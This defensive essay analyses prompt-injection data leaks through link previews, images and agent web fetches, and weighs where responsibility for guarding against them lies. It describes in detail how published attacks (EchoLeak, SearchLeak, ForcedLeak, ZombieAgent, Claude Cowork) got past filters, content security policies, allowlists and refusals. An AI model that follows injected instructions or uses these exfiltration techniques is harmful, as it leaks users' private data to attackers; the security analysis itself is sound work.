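Most offices would put up with software that failed at random once in 500 uses, but an attacker can cause the failure deliberately by choosing the wording and trying again after each refusal.

If every attempt had the same independent chance *p* of success, an attacker with *k* attempts would succeed at least once with probability 1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*. For Opus 5, with *p* at 0.2%, 15 attempts would give about 3%, a little above the measured 2.0%. For Opus 4.5, 100 attempts at 4.7% would give more than 99%, but the measured rate was 63%. Attempts are evidently not independent, probably because a model that resists one attack in a given scenario tends to resist the next. Retrying therefore helps an attacker less than it would if attempts were independent, though it still raised the success rate against Opus 5 tenfold.

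The attacker may also not care which company leaks. Suppose the poisoned brochure reaches 1,000 firms whose agents each have a 0.2% chance of following its instructions. On average two of them leak something, and if the chances are independent, the probability of at least one leak is about 86%. If the firms all use the same model, a given wording will probably fail nearly everywhere or work at many firms at once. Previews make it easier for the attacker to find a wording that works, because the attacker can confirm a success from a visit in the server's log. Failed attempts carry some risk, since a model that recognises an injection can warn its user.

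### The argument that models may always be vulnerable

Researchers disagree about whether better training could eventually bring the rate to zero. In *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026) argue that looking for instructions hidden in data is the wrong approach to defence. An agent that handles email has to act on what emails contain. If a message requests a travel refund and says the department head approved it, the agent can't tell from the text whether the department head did.

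The analysis uses contextual integrity, the philosopher Helen Nissenbaum's theory of privacy. It judges a flow of information by the norms of its setting, which specify the sender, the receiver, the person the information is about, the type of information, and the conditions under which it may be shared. An attacker succeeds by getting the agent to act on a false claim about one of these, for example that the user has already given permission.

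Suppose an agent acts with probability *p* when it sees certain evidence. The evidence could be genuine, in which case the action is appropriate, or forged by an attacker. The agent can't tell which, so *p* is the same in both cases. It carries out the attack with probability *p* if the evidence is forged, and blocks the legitimate action with probability 1 − *p* if the evidence is genuine. These probabilities add up to 1, so at least one of the two errors has a probability of 50% or more.

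The proof is correct, but it assumes that the two situations look identical to the agent. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian acknowledge that this may not hold in every deployment and that a trusted check can remove the ambiguity. They expect such ambiguity to become more common as agents work with less supervision. The theorem therefore describes a trade-off that some agents will face, but not necessarily all.

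Their experiments show that the ambiguity is easy to create. They gave an email assistant read-only tasks, such as summarising the inbox, and had a second model write emails intended to make it send a reply. For each of 150 scenarios, the attacking model had three separate runs of up to 15 tries, and it revised its email after each failure. It succeeded in 96.7% of the scenarios, compared with 0.67% for the original emails. The most common method was to forge an earlier message from the user. Both models were Claude Sonnet 4.6, but the best emails also worked without changes on GPT-5.4 in 63.3% of cases and on Gemini 3 Pro in 92.6%.

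The set-up favoured the attacker, who could read the assistant's standing instructions. Those instructions told the assistant to send emails when appropriate without asking the user. The models were also older than Opus 5. But retries explain only part of the result, since the attacker's first email succeeded 61.4% of the time. A low success rate on a fixed set of attacks evidently doesn't guarantee a low rate against an attacker who writes new ones for a specific agent.

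Screening the incoming text wouldn't have helped much either. Slack suggests checking prompts with a smaller model or fixed rules before the main model reads them. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian tested two such classifiers on pairs of emails that differed only in whether one clause falsely claimed authority. The classifiers scored 0.43 and 0.59 on a scale where 0.5 is guessing. A Llama model trained to resist injections sent unauthorised replies to these emails 88.2% of the time, compared with 54.0% for the original model. The original already performed poorly, so the result raises concern about this kind of training but doesn't show that all such training fails.

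The experiments concern unauthorised emails. The trade-off is less severe for a link containing an alarm code, because a reply rarely has a good reason to put a private note into the address of an outside site. A model could refuse to write such links and disappoint few users. Explicit rules seem to help. In another experiment, an email thread combined a permitted internal task with a message to an outsider that the user had not approved. GPT-5.4 sent the message in 34% of scenarios and Sonnet 4.6 in 6%. When the user stated that external communication needed approval, both rates fell to zero, although GPT-5.2 still sent it in 12%. Slack recommends a similar system prompt rule, against writing URLs with sensitive data in the query string, but describes this kind of hardening as "not a complete solution".

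But the model has little information about who will receive the data. The reply goes to the office manager, who is allowed to know the code, and unless someone has told the model about link previews, nothing in its context suggests that Slack will contact example.com first. The model could apply Nissenbaum's theory perfectly to the facts it has and still leak the code. Switching previews off prevents this leak regardless of the model's judgment. The theorem doesn't rule out this fix, because nobody has to work out whether the message is genuine. There is therefore a much stronger case for holding the builder responsible for the code around the model than for the model's training.

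### Objections to relying on the builder

Getting the code right can take more than changing two settings. A builder whose agent posts to ten apps has to know how each one treats links, and the platforms don't always make this easy to learn. Kemple's *Data & security best practices for agentic Slack apps*, a post for Slack's developers that he updated in April 2026, covers passwords, permissions and the approval of new apps. It doesn't mention link previews, so a builder could follow all of its advice and still release an agent that leaks data. It also lists `chat:write`, the permission to post messages, among the low-risk permissions that a company can always allow.

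Builders can reply that they already write separate code for each app, because each accepts messages differently, and that the preview setting belongs in that code. Where a builder doesn't know how an app behaves, the agent can post without links until somebody has checked. This protects users but inconveniences them, and a builder competing for those users may not want to do that.

A builder's knowledge of a platform can also go out of date. Telegram's change log for bots lists additions to "rich messages", a newer message format, in versions 10.2, 10.3 and 10.4. Each new format adds another way for a message to display outside content, and a setting that covered the old format may not cover the new one. A builder can test for this by posting a link to a server it controls and checking the server's log for visits. Running the test before every release would catch most changes, but the platform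 can still change its behaviour after a release.

If a platform has no setting for link previews, the builder can still remove links or decline to support the platform. Removing links gives the builder full control over the leak, but it makes legitimate replies less useful because of a feature that belongs to the platform. A company that connects the agent through another firm's connector may not have even this choice if it can't change how the connector posts.

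Abandoned connectors are the hardest case for this view, because a duty on the builder is of little use once the builder stops maintaining the software. Anthropic's Slack connector, the subject of CVE-2025-34072, stayed in use with previews on after Anthropic had stopped maintaining it. Slack administrators can require approval for every new app, but Slack also describes rules that automatically approve apps requesting only low-risk permissions. An unmaintained connector that only posts messages would pass those rules.

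The best reply is that builders should turn previews off in the first version, because people who install a connector mostly keep its defaults, and those defaults remain after maintenance ends. If Anthropic had done this at the start, it could have retired the connector without leaving this flaw behind. This is good advice for new connectors, but it doesn't fix the copies already running. Their owners have to find and change those copies unless the platform stops fetching the links.

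## The view that the displaying platform should treat agent messages as untrusted

Making the rendering platform responsible is attractive in practice because one change can protect every copy of a vulnerable tool. For example, if Slack stopped fetching links in messages from apps, link previews would stop leaking data from all copies of Anthropic's abandoned connector at once.

Another argument for this view is that text does nothing until a program interprets it. The link in the alarm code example leaks the code only because Slack interprets it as a URL and fetches it. Slack decides which characters make a link and which links get a preview, and it doesn't fully document these rules for builders.

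Slack never previews a link whose visible label is part of its address, such as "example.com" for `http://example.com`. A builder might label links this way to suppress previews. But according to the same documentation, Slack's servers fetch every address in a message, and it doesn't specify whether these links are an exception.

### The precedent of cross-site scripting

Web developers neutralise code in visitors' comments to prevent cross-site scripting, or XSS, which attackers can use to take over accounts and steal data.

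The accepted defence is to encode the comment before displaying it. The site replaces `<`, which opens an HTML tag, with `&lt;`, which the browser shows as "<". The right encoding depends on where the text will appear, because browsers read HTML, JavaScript, style rules and addresses differently. For example, HTML encoding works in the body of a page but fails inside an event handler (an attribute containing JavaScript), because the browser decodes the HTML before running the JavaScript.

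OWASP's *Cross Site Scripting Prevention Cheat Sheet* advises developers to encode data as close as possible to where the page displays it. It warns against relying on a filter that cleans data when it first reaches the application, because it isn't yet clear at that point whether a surname, for example, will appear between two tags or inside a script. Changing text after cleaning it can also undo the protection.

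An agent's connector is in much the same position as that early filter. It handles the reply before Slack decides how to display it, and the reply may later appear in a notification or email digest that the connector's builder never considered. The XSS precedent fits the platform better than the builder, although supporters of the builder's duty also cite it. On a site with comments, whoever builds the page encodes them, and Slack builds the page that displays the agent's message.

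Encoding doesn't carry over as well to agent messages, because it prevents text from acting as code, and a data-carrying link is dangerous even when it works as a normal link. Standard encoding for addresses would leave `HERON-4417` unchanged, because it contains only letters, digits and a hyphen. OWASP's advice to use "safe sinks" does carry over. These are places in a page where the browser treats whatever it receives as plain text, so a developer who uses one doesn't have to work out whether the text is malicious. The equivalent for an agent's message would be a display that shows the words and the link but fetches nothing.

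### Whom OWASP's entry on model output is for

OWASP also publishes a list of the ten main risks in applications built on language models. One entry, *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, covers applications that don't sufficiently check or clean a model's output before passing it to other components. It advises developers to treat the model like any other user, encode its output for the place where it will be used, and set a strict Content Security Policy (CSP), which tells the browser where a web app may load images and other resources from. In one scenario, close to the alarm code example, a tool that summarises websites processes a page containing a prompt injection and sends private data to an attacker's server, with no check on the output.

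The advice is for whoever runs the application that contains the model. If that application also displays the replies, as a company's own chatbot page does, one party is responsible for everything. But when an agent posts to Slack, Slack is downstream, and under the entry the message should be checked before it gets there. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026) matches the entry to CWE-116, a category in a standard catalogue of software weaknesses. CWE-116 covers programs that fail to encode what they send to another component, so it also places the fault with the sender.

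OWASP's list for language models leans towards holding the builder responsible, while its older advice on XSS leans towards the platform. A developer at a messaging company could read the list and reasonably conclude that this entry didn't apply to them. The 2026 edition probably won't change that. It keeps the category but moves it from fifth place to last, according to SC Media's *OWASP updates Top 10 security risks for LLM applications*. Citadelo's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) reports that the new edition also tells developers to design systems assuming that the model will be fooled. A platform could assume the same of every agent that posts to it.

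### What a platform can change

A platform has several ways to act on the assumption. Each blocks some requests and leaves others alone.

| Measure | What it stops | What it doesn't stop |
|---|---|---|
| No previews for bot messages by default | The fetch on delivery | Clicks; images inside the message; bots that turn previews on |
| Previews off in chosen channels | The fetch on delivery in those channels | The same fetch in any other channel the agent can post in |
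| CSP limits on image sources | The reader's browser loading images from unlisted hosts | Clicks; requests by the platform's servers; leaks through listed hosts |
| Image proxy | The site learning the reader's internet address | Delivery of any data in the image's address |
| Warning before a link opens | Some clicks | Any automatic fetch |

The new default would help abandoned software the most. Slack could keep its existing settings and default to "off" for an app that sets neither, so a builder who wanted previews would have to turn them on. This would not protect an app whose builder turns on previews because they look good and then lets a model write the links.

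Turning previews off by channel works only if the setting covers every place the agent can post, including direct messages. An administrator would naturally turn previews off in the finance channel and leave them on in the one for lunch plans. If the agent can post in both, an attacker can use the injection to direct it to the lunch channel.

A CSP restricts the reader's browser but not Slack's servers, so it wouldn't have stopped a link preview from leaking the alarm code. It is more useful against leaks through images, but it has limits. An entry can name a particular folder on a host, but after a redirect the browser checks only the host, as trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* points out. An image proxy can also weaken a CSP. If the proxy is on the list of permitted hosts, the browser permits every image that goes through it, so the proxy protects data only if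 it refuses to fetch some addresses.

Warnings depend on the reader to judge whether a link is safe. To help against a link that carries data, a warning has to show the whole address, including a query string that the reader may not understand. If the platform shows a warning for every link, people will soon click through without reading.

Some companies that run their own assistants go further and remove links from the reply. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* describes an assistant that redacts every address until an administrator adds it to a trusted list. The policy in Glean's *Untrusted URL monitoring* keeps a link if it came from a trusted tool, is on a trusted domain, or appeared in the user's own message. It classes a link as fabricated if it appears in neither the conversation nor the results from the agent's tools, which would catch the alarm code link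 if the brochure contained only instructions for building it. Glean can make this check because it has both, whereas Slack and Telegram receive only the finished message from an outside agent.

### Permitted hosts that strangers could use

Companies have tried several of these guards, starting with simple ones. In 2023 Rehberger reported to Microsoft that images in Bing Chat's replies could leak a conversation. That May, Microsoft added a CSP header that generally prevented images from loading, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. OpenAI received a report of the same problem in ChatGPT and added its first protection that December. A guard in the display has to be in every program that displays the message, but OpenAI left this one out of some, including its macOS and iOS apps.

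Blocking nearly all outside images is crude, and most companies want to allow some. Google limited images in Bard, its chatbot at the time, to hosts under google.com. Willison explained in *Hacking Google Bard* that one of those hosts was script.google.com, where anyone can run a small program, so an attacker could receive the data at a Google address.

Salesforce made a different mistake with Agentforce, its system for building agents that work with customer records. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) reposts the full report by Noma Labs, the security researchers who found the flaw. Their attack began with a web form that companies use to collect enquiries from potential customers. The form's description field accepts 42,000 characters, enough room for injected instructions. When an employee later asked the agent to deal with the enquiry, the agent also looked up other potential customers' email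 addresses and put them in an image URL.

Salesforce's CSP failed to block the image because its list of permitted hosts included my-salesforce-cms.com, a domain whose registration had lapsed and which Noma had bought for $5. Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025. Salesforce recovered the domain and, on 8 September, began enforcing a list of trusted addresses for its agents' output, according to the news site Salesforce Ben. Noma published its findings on 25 September.

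Salesforce's list also permitted every host under amazonaws.com, where Amazon's customers store files and run servers. Anyone can become a customer, so an attacker might have been able to use an ordinary Amazon account instead of the expired domain. Noma didn't report testing this.

The mail app Superhuman had a CSP that allowed images from docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms. A Google Form can be filled in and submitted by requesting a URL that contains the answers. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack that used this. A user asks the assistant to summarize recent mail, and one unopened email contains a prompt injection. The injection makes the assistant put the contents of other emails into the URL of the attacker's form and display that URL as an image. When the browser tries to load the image, it submits the form to the attacker. A single reply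 leaked parts of more than 40 emails.

PromptArmor reported the problem to Superhuman on a Friday night in December 2025, and Superhuman switched off the vulnerable features on Monday. The fixes continued into January because the problem went beyond one line in a CSP. Superhuman Go, a related product, loaded images directly from an attacker's domain. The mail assistant could also open web pages itself. An injection could make it visit a link containing data without displaying anything, so limits on displayed images would not have stopped the request.

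The form trick worked again on OpenAI's Codex in April 2026, three months after PromptArmor published it. OpenAI has since fixed the flaw, according to PromptArmor's *Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data*. Salesforce's instructions for Agentforce Coworker still use docs.google.com as their example of a trusted address. An administrator who copies the example allows links to a host where a click can submit a stranger's form. If Coworker also loads images from trusted addresses, it may submit the form without a click.

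### Guards that came too early or too late

Microsoft 365 Copilot had more protection than any of these products, and researchers got past it twice in about a year. Aim Labs found the first flaw, EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), in January 2025. An attacker only had to send the victim an email. When Copilot later retrieved that email to answer a question from the victim, the email's injected instructions were to put the most sensitive information Copilot had in a link.

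Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, describes how the attack bypassed each safeguard. Microsoft screened incoming text for injections, but the attacker addressed the email's instructions to the human recipient and never mentioned an AI, so the classifier missed them. Copilot also removed outside links from its replies, using a filter that recognised links in Markdown, a simple formatting language, when the address came straight after the link's text. Markdown also allows the address to go on a separate line further down. The filter missed that form, but the display still turned it into a working link. The same form worked for images, which load without a click.

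That left the CSP, which blocked images from the attacker's own site. Aim Labs searched the permitted hosts for one that would pass the request on. A SharePoint service did so, but only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A Teams service did so without an invitation. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, identify it as a preview service, which Microsoft had built to fetch content for links. The request got past the CSP because the browser sent it to Microsoft, whose server then contacted the attacker's.

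The second flaw, SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824), began with a link to Microsoft's own site. The link's address contained a prompt, which Copilot's search page ran as soon as the victim clicked. In Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026), Copilot finds an email, takes its title, which may contain a login code, and writes it into the address of an image. Microsoft's defence was to wrap Copilot's output in a code block, which is sound because it makes the browser show an image's code as text. But Copilot added the wrapping only when the reply was complete, and the browser displayed the reply as it arrived, so the browser requested the image before the wrapping was in place.

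The CSP failed as it had in EchoLeak, by permitting a host that could relay requests. This time the host was bing.com, whose search-by-image feature fetches any address it receives. Bing.com was already on Copilot's list of permitted image hosts when Ravia published the list a year earlier. Microsoft had fixed EchoLeak without removing, or perhaps without checking for, every other host that could relay a request. Varonis advises companies to check their own lists for such hosts.

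In all four cases the browser contacted only hosts that the CSP permitted, but the safety of the data depended on who could receive it through those hosts. A lapsed domain had a new owner, a Google address passed data to whoever had made the form, and two Microsoft services forwarded requests to anyone. OWASP recommends a CSP only as an extra layer against XSS, partly because it is easy to get wrong. Companies that use a CSP to prevent data leaks could follow trackr.live's advice to approve a particular resource and its owner, and to refuse any service that will fetch an address supplied by someone else.

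The failures of Copilot's filters support the case for a check at the point of display. In EchoLeak, the filter and the display parsed the same Markdown differently, and in SearchLeak, the display acted on the output before the filter did. Varonis recommends sanitizing a model's output when it is displayed, which closely matches OWASP's advice on XSS. But making the right company responsible is not enough. Microsoft, Salesforce and Superhuman each controlled both the assistant and its display and knew that a model was writing the replies, yet each left a gap.

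These companies could at least close the gap for everyone. Microsoft fixed EchoLeak on its own servers in May 2025, so its customers had nothing to install. Reddy and Gujral report no evidence that attackers had exploited the flaw. Anthropic had no comparable way to fix the copies of its Slack connector on other people's machines.

### Messages from bots and from people

A platform can't tell from a message's text whether a model or a person wrote it, which is a common objection to this view. But the platform usually knows how the message arrived. Bots post to Slack and Telegram through interfaces made for software, and a platform could apply a stricter rule to everything that arrives this way without working out which bots contain a language model.

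The objection is stronger when an agent uses a person's account. Some apps post under a user's name with the user's permission, and the platform can still recognise those messages if they come through the developer interface. But an agent that controls a browser types into the message box the same way a person does. Copilot Cowork sends email through Outlook on its user's behalf, and the recipient's mail provider receives what looks like ordinary mail from an employee. People also paste an agent's answer, including its link, into a chat themselves.

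A rule for bots would not cover any of these cases. To cover them, a platform would have to stop automatic fetches for everyone, perhaps by loading a preview only when a reader asks for it. That much larger change would affect millions of people who have never used an agent. The rule for bots still seems worth having, since it would have covered both the Slack connector and OpenClaw on Telegram.

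### What people would lose

Previews also help readers decide whether to open a link. A title and picture can show that a colleague has pasted a link to last year's budget by mistake. But they are a poor way to spot a malicious link, because the attacker controls the page and can choose a reassuring title and picture, like the shelving in the alarm code example.

A platform can give readers some of this help without contacting the site. It can show the link's domain name next to it, so that friendly link text doesn't hide an unfamiliar destination. Fetching only the site's home page, without the rest of the address, can still leak data. An attacker can put the data in the domain name itself, as in `heron-4417.example.com`, and any request to that host would deliver it.

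Bots without a language model need previews too. A support bot may post links to tickets, and a monitoring bot may post graphs. Some of these messages closely resemble an attack. Chart services such as QuickChart read a chart's figures from the image's address, so a bot that posts a sales graph this way sends the sales figures to another company on purpose. A platform that tried to recognise leaks by how an address looks would block the graph too.

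Simple bots mostly link to a few sites that their developers can name in advance, and Slack already has a procedure that could suit them. An app that wants to supply its own link previews registers up to five domains, and whoever installs the app agrees to them. If the developer adds another domain, the workspace must reinstall the app. The procedure currently covers links that people post, but Slack could extend it so that a bot's messages get previews only for the domains on its list. The list would need the same care as a Content Security Policy (CSP), since an attacker could also use a shared host on it.

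This would suit a ticket bot much better than a research agent, whose links may lead anywhere. The research agent would lose most previews, though its readers could still open the links. Older bots would also lose their previews until someone updated them, and unmaintained ones would lose them permanently. That loss matters to people who rely on the pictures, but it is much less serious than an unmaintained connector that can still send out an access key.

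## The view that the guard belongs where the request is made

A third view puts the guard at the machine that makes the network request. The other two, cleaning an agent's output and distrusting it on display, both depend on somebody handling a dangerous message correctly. However an attacker words an injection, the data leaves only when some machine requests an address. That machine has the full address, so it can check it against a list, refuse the request, or ask a person first. trackr.live argues for this view on the grounds that natural language is unbounded, while a company can list the destinations it permits for fetches. On this view, filtering incoming text is still worth doing, but only as an extra layer.

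On this view, whoever runs the machine that makes the request is responsible for security. If an agent opens web pages from a company's own server, the company can put a firewall in front of that server. OpenAI makes the request when ChatGPT opens a page, and Slack makes it when Slack builds a preview.

### Checking the destination instead of the wording

Defences that rely on wording can be fragile. In *The Framing Gap* (2026), an injection got a model to leak a secret in 31.9% of trials. A policy that forbade revealing the secret "in any form" cut this to zero, but the leak rate was 48.8% under a policy that named specific behaviours without that catch-all. A separate detector caught every reworded attack with no false alarms. But detectors vary a lot, and the two that Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian tested on forged emails did little better than guessing.

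Sometimes malicious instructions come from the user, so there is no injection to detect. In February 2026, a researcher at Anthropic ran an exercise in which an employee received an email with a prompt to paste into Claude Code. Along with ordinary setup steps, the prompt included instructions to read a file of Amazon cloud credentials and send the contents to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. Safeguards based on the user's intent had no basis for flagging the instructions because the user had entered them. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* concludes that only limits on the agent's environment, such as egress controls and restricted file access, would have prevented this.

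Willison describes three conditions that together make an agent dangerous: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. The third is generally the easiest to remove. In the alarm code example, the office manager wants the agent to read both the brochure and the company's notes, but loses very little if the agent can't contact a stranger's server.

Many agents don't yet have such a check. According to *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026), users of current frameworks grant permission tool by tool, so a user who approves "web search" approves every address the tool will request. The interface may also shorten the addresses it shows, which hides the part that contains the data.

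### An experiment with 480 runs

In *Silent Egress* (2026), Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay measured how often an agent sends out a secret and which defences stop it. They put a secret directly in the context of qwen2.5:7b, a small model that anyone can download. The user always asked for a summary of a web page. The agent's software automatically loaded the page's title, description and text, one of which contained an injection. The agent also had a tool for making web requests.

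The attacker's server received a request in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88% (the abstract gives 89%). It received none in 120 runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's reply was innocuous, so a check of the reply alone would have missed them.

Here, previews brought the injection in and a tool call sent the data out, whereas in the alarm code example the brochure brings the injection in and Slack's preview sends the data out. The 88% is therefore not an estimate of how often a messaging app leaks data. The 95% doesn't apply to Slack either, because a data-carrying link posted there is part of the reply, where a check could find it.

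Lan and colleagues then added defences to a version of the attack that had always succeeded, with 30 runs for each.

| Defence | Agent tried to send the secret | Attacker received a request |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Instruction to treat web content as data | 67% | 67% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Instruction and tags together | 57% | 57% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
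| Filter for suspicious domains and paths | 83% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 23% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |

More than half of the attacks still worked against the defences in the prompt. Adding tags to the instruction reduced the number of successful attacks from 20 to 17, a difference that could easily be chance. With the allowlist, the agent tried every time and was blocked each time. This is the clearest result in the table, but it is nearly true by definition, because the researchers chose a domain that no sensible company would have on its list. The test of the filter for suspicious paths was also easy, since the filter blocked the word "collect" and the paper's sample attack uses that word.

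The last two rows are harder to believe. A filter on outgoing requests runs outside the model, so it shouldn't change what the model first tries to do, yet the attempts fell from 30 out of 30 to seven and then to none. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model sometimes disguised the secret, but a disguised secret should have got past a word filter and reached the attacker. Something else probably differed between the conditions.

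The experiment also shows why checking destinations is more reliable than scanning for secrets. In half of the 480 runs, the injection contained instructions to split the secret into four pieces and send them separately. This succeeded in 185 of 240 runs, compared with 238 when the secret was sent in one piece. But a scanner would probably miss a four-character fragment because it has no recognizable pattern. An allowlist blocks all four pieces if the attacker's site isn't on it.

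Lan and colleagues acknowledge that their set-up favoured the attacker, because the system prompt was minimal and the secret was in plain view. They also call their success rate a lower bound because the injections were crude, but it can hardly be one for newer models, some of which resist injection far better.

### From trusted sites to exact addresses

OpenAI arrived at its present method after several simpler rules failed. In December 2023, it added a check to ChatGPT that queried OpenAI's servers to determine whether a link was safe. OpenAI didn't publish the criteria, but researchers worked out some of them by trial and error. Tenable (2025) found that the check always approved addresses at bing.com. Bing's search results use bing.com links that forward visitors to the listed sites, so an attacker whose pages appeared in the results had approved links to them. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating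 Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* demonstrated another bypass.

OpenAI tightened the check around August 2025. That year, in *ShadowLeak*, the security firm Radware got ChatGPT's Deep Research agent to leak data from OpenAI's own servers. The agent refused several versions of the request before Radware found one that worked. OpenAI responded by allowing ChatGPT to open links only exactly as it had received them.

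Radware's *ZombieAgent* got around that rule without breaking it. The attacker's email supplied a set of ready-made web addresses, each standing for one character, and ChatGPT spelled out the private data by opening them in order. Radware reported this on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT would no longer open every link from an email, though it could still open one that appeared in a well-known public index.

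In January 2026, OpenAI described a general method based on the same idea:

1. A crawler visits public web pages, as a search engine's does, and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When an agent is about to fetch a page or image automatically, software looks for that exact address in the crawler's records.
3. If the address is there, the agent fetches it.
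4. If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try another site or warns the user. The warning explains that nobody has verified the link and that it may contain information from the conversation.

A list of trusted domains restricts only the domain, so an attacker can put data in the rest of the address. The exact match requires the whole address to be one the crawler has already recorded. The crawler can't have recorded `example.com/details?ref=HERON-4417` unless somebody had already published the alarm code, so the link fails the check even if example.com is on the trusted list.

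Redirects also matter less. An attacker may find a link on a trusted domain that forwards a visitor, along with any data in the address, to an untrusted site. A recorded address can also forward a visitor, but it existed before the conversation and so contains nothing from it. Attackers can get their own pages into the crawler's records, but they have to choose the addresses before they know the secret.

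The method has drawbacks. The records may not yet include a page published this morning, and they shouldn't include a private link to a shared document. In either case, the agent has to give up on the page or interrupt the user. OpenAI objects to strict domain lists because frequent warnings train people to click through them, and this applies equally to warnings about unrecorded addresses. Anthropic found that users approved about 93% of Claude Code's permission requests. Most of those requests were presumably fine, so 93% isn't an error rate, but a person who approves nearly everything will probably approve the rare bad request too.

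OpenAI's paper *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents* gives the technical details. In Embrace The Red's account, Rehberger calls the method a significant improvement but not a complete solution. He also worries that some of OpenAI's developers won't know about the check and will release features without it. This seems a fair concern, since OpenAI left the first version out of some of its apps. Neither Embrace The Red's account nor OpenAI's announcement reports how often attacks succeed against the method.

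### Addresses that Claude has already seen

Anthropic uses a rule that doesn't require a crawler. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, Claude can fetch an address only if it has already appeared in the conversation, whether in the user's message, in a result from one of the developer's own tools, or in an earlier web search or fetch. Claude therefore can't fetch an address it has made up, such as the alarm code link. The rule also works for a page that went online five minutes ago, if the user supplies the link.

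When Anthropic introduced the tool in September 2025, Willison noticed a weakness in the first of these sources. Many applications paste emails or documents into the user's message, so an attacker's links can count as the user's own.

Ayush Paul found a more serious hole in Claude's chat app in July 2026. As Willison (2026) explains, Claude could also follow links on pages it had already fetched. Paul built a website with a link for each letter of the alphabet and persuaded Claude to spell out facts about its user by following them, which revealed the user's name, home city and employer. The site showed the trap only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking it would have seen nothing odd. As *The Read-Only Lie*, a post by אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם, points out, the tool could only read pages, but its choice of pages sent information to the site.

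Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and it paid no bounty. It fixed the problem by stopping Claude from following links on the pages it fetches. This makes Claude less useful for browsing, since people rely heavily on links when they use the web.

Developers who build on Claude still have the older arrangement by default. In November 2026, Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, the Chinese edition of its documentation, listed earlier fetches among the permitted sources of addresses, although developers could switch off each source separately. Those who keep the default seem to accept the risk that Anthropic removed from its own app. The default also accepts an address from a developer's tool when the tool has only repeated something Claude wrote, for example in an error message. The fetch tool refuses addresses that appear to contain a password or key the user didn't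 supply, but it might not recognise `HERON-4417` as either.

| Rule | Effect on the alarm code link | How data can still get out | What it hinders |
|---|---|---|---|
| Trusted domains | Blocks it only if example.com is off the list | Through a listed site that forwards, stores or logs what it receives | Browsing beyond the list |
| Addresses already in the conversation | Blocks it | By a choice among links that the attacker supplies | Building new addresses, such as a filtered search |
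| Addresses in a public index | Blocks it | By a choice among pages that the attacker had indexed beforehand | Opening new pages and private links |

### What a choice of address can reveal

The last two rules can both leak data, and no list of exact addresses can fully prevent this. If an agent may fetch any of *N* addresses, and the attacker can see which one it fetched, one request can reveal up to log₂ *N* bits, and *k* requests can reveal up to *k* × log₂ *N* bits. Leaking `HERON-4417` takes ten requests if there is one address for each letter, digit and the hyphen, but only six if there are a thousand addresses.

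Some secrets are smaller than that. Whether a company plans to accept a takeover bid is one bit of information, and an agent can reveal it by choosing between two ordinary pages.

Rehberger described the technique in 2023. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) reported that ChatGPT would open only ten addresses per prompt, which limited the attack to ten characters at a time. The same idea then worked against ChatGPT in 2025 and Claude in 2026, after both companies had stopped their models from fetching addresses the models had constructed themselves. Embrace The Red reports that OpenAI's paper acknowledges the remaining leak.

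A guard can slow the leak. Anthropic's tool lets developers cap the number of fetches, though it sets no cap by default. Rehberger suggests that an agent should never request the same address twice in a session, or should keep a copy of each response for a few minutes, so that a repeated letter produces no second visit. Radware's attack already used separate addresses for each position in the text, so an attacker facing such a rule would mainly need more pages. OpenAI's method would require all those pages to be in the index first.

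Even so, the exact-address rules make stealing data much harder. Without them, an attacker can send out thousands of characters in one request. The rules force attackers to rely on a model that follows their instructions, a prepared set of pages and a long run of requests that somebody might notice. A password could still get out this way, but copying a whole contract would take a very long time.

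### Permitted services that an attacker can also use

Companies that run agents on their own machines more often use a list of allowed domains, which can fail in the same way as a CSP. Willison gives the example of Antigravity, Google's programming tool, whose browser could visit only listed domains. The default list included webhook.site, a service that records incoming requests and shows them to whoever set up the page.

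Anthropic made a subtler mistake with Claude Cowork, a desktop agent for office work that is separate from Microsoft's Copilot Cowork. Claude Cowork runs code in a virtual machine, a sealed-off computer simulated in software. The virtual machine could reach only a short list of domains, which had to include api.anthropic.com because the product doesn't work without Anthropic's service. But any customer can also use that service to upload files to an account.

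Rehberger had already used the upload feature to extract data from Claude's chat app, in Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*. Anthropic acknowledged the problem but released Claude Cowork in January 2026 without fixing it. Two days later, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated the attack on the new product. A user gave Cowork a folder of property documents and a Word file disguised as a skill. The Word file contained an injection in tiny white text, along with the attacker's key to Anthropic's service. Cowork used that key to upload the largest document to the attacker's account without asking for approval. The document included financial figures and parts of social security numbers.

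The egress control had worked as designed. Anthropic now describes an allowlist as a "capability grant", because permitting a domain permits everything anyone can do there. Its fix was a proxy inside the virtual machine that checks each request to api.anthropic.com and forwards only those carrying that machine's own session token, so an upload with somebody else's key fails. Anthropic put the proxy inside the virtual machine because its servers can't tell a Cowork request from any other customer's.

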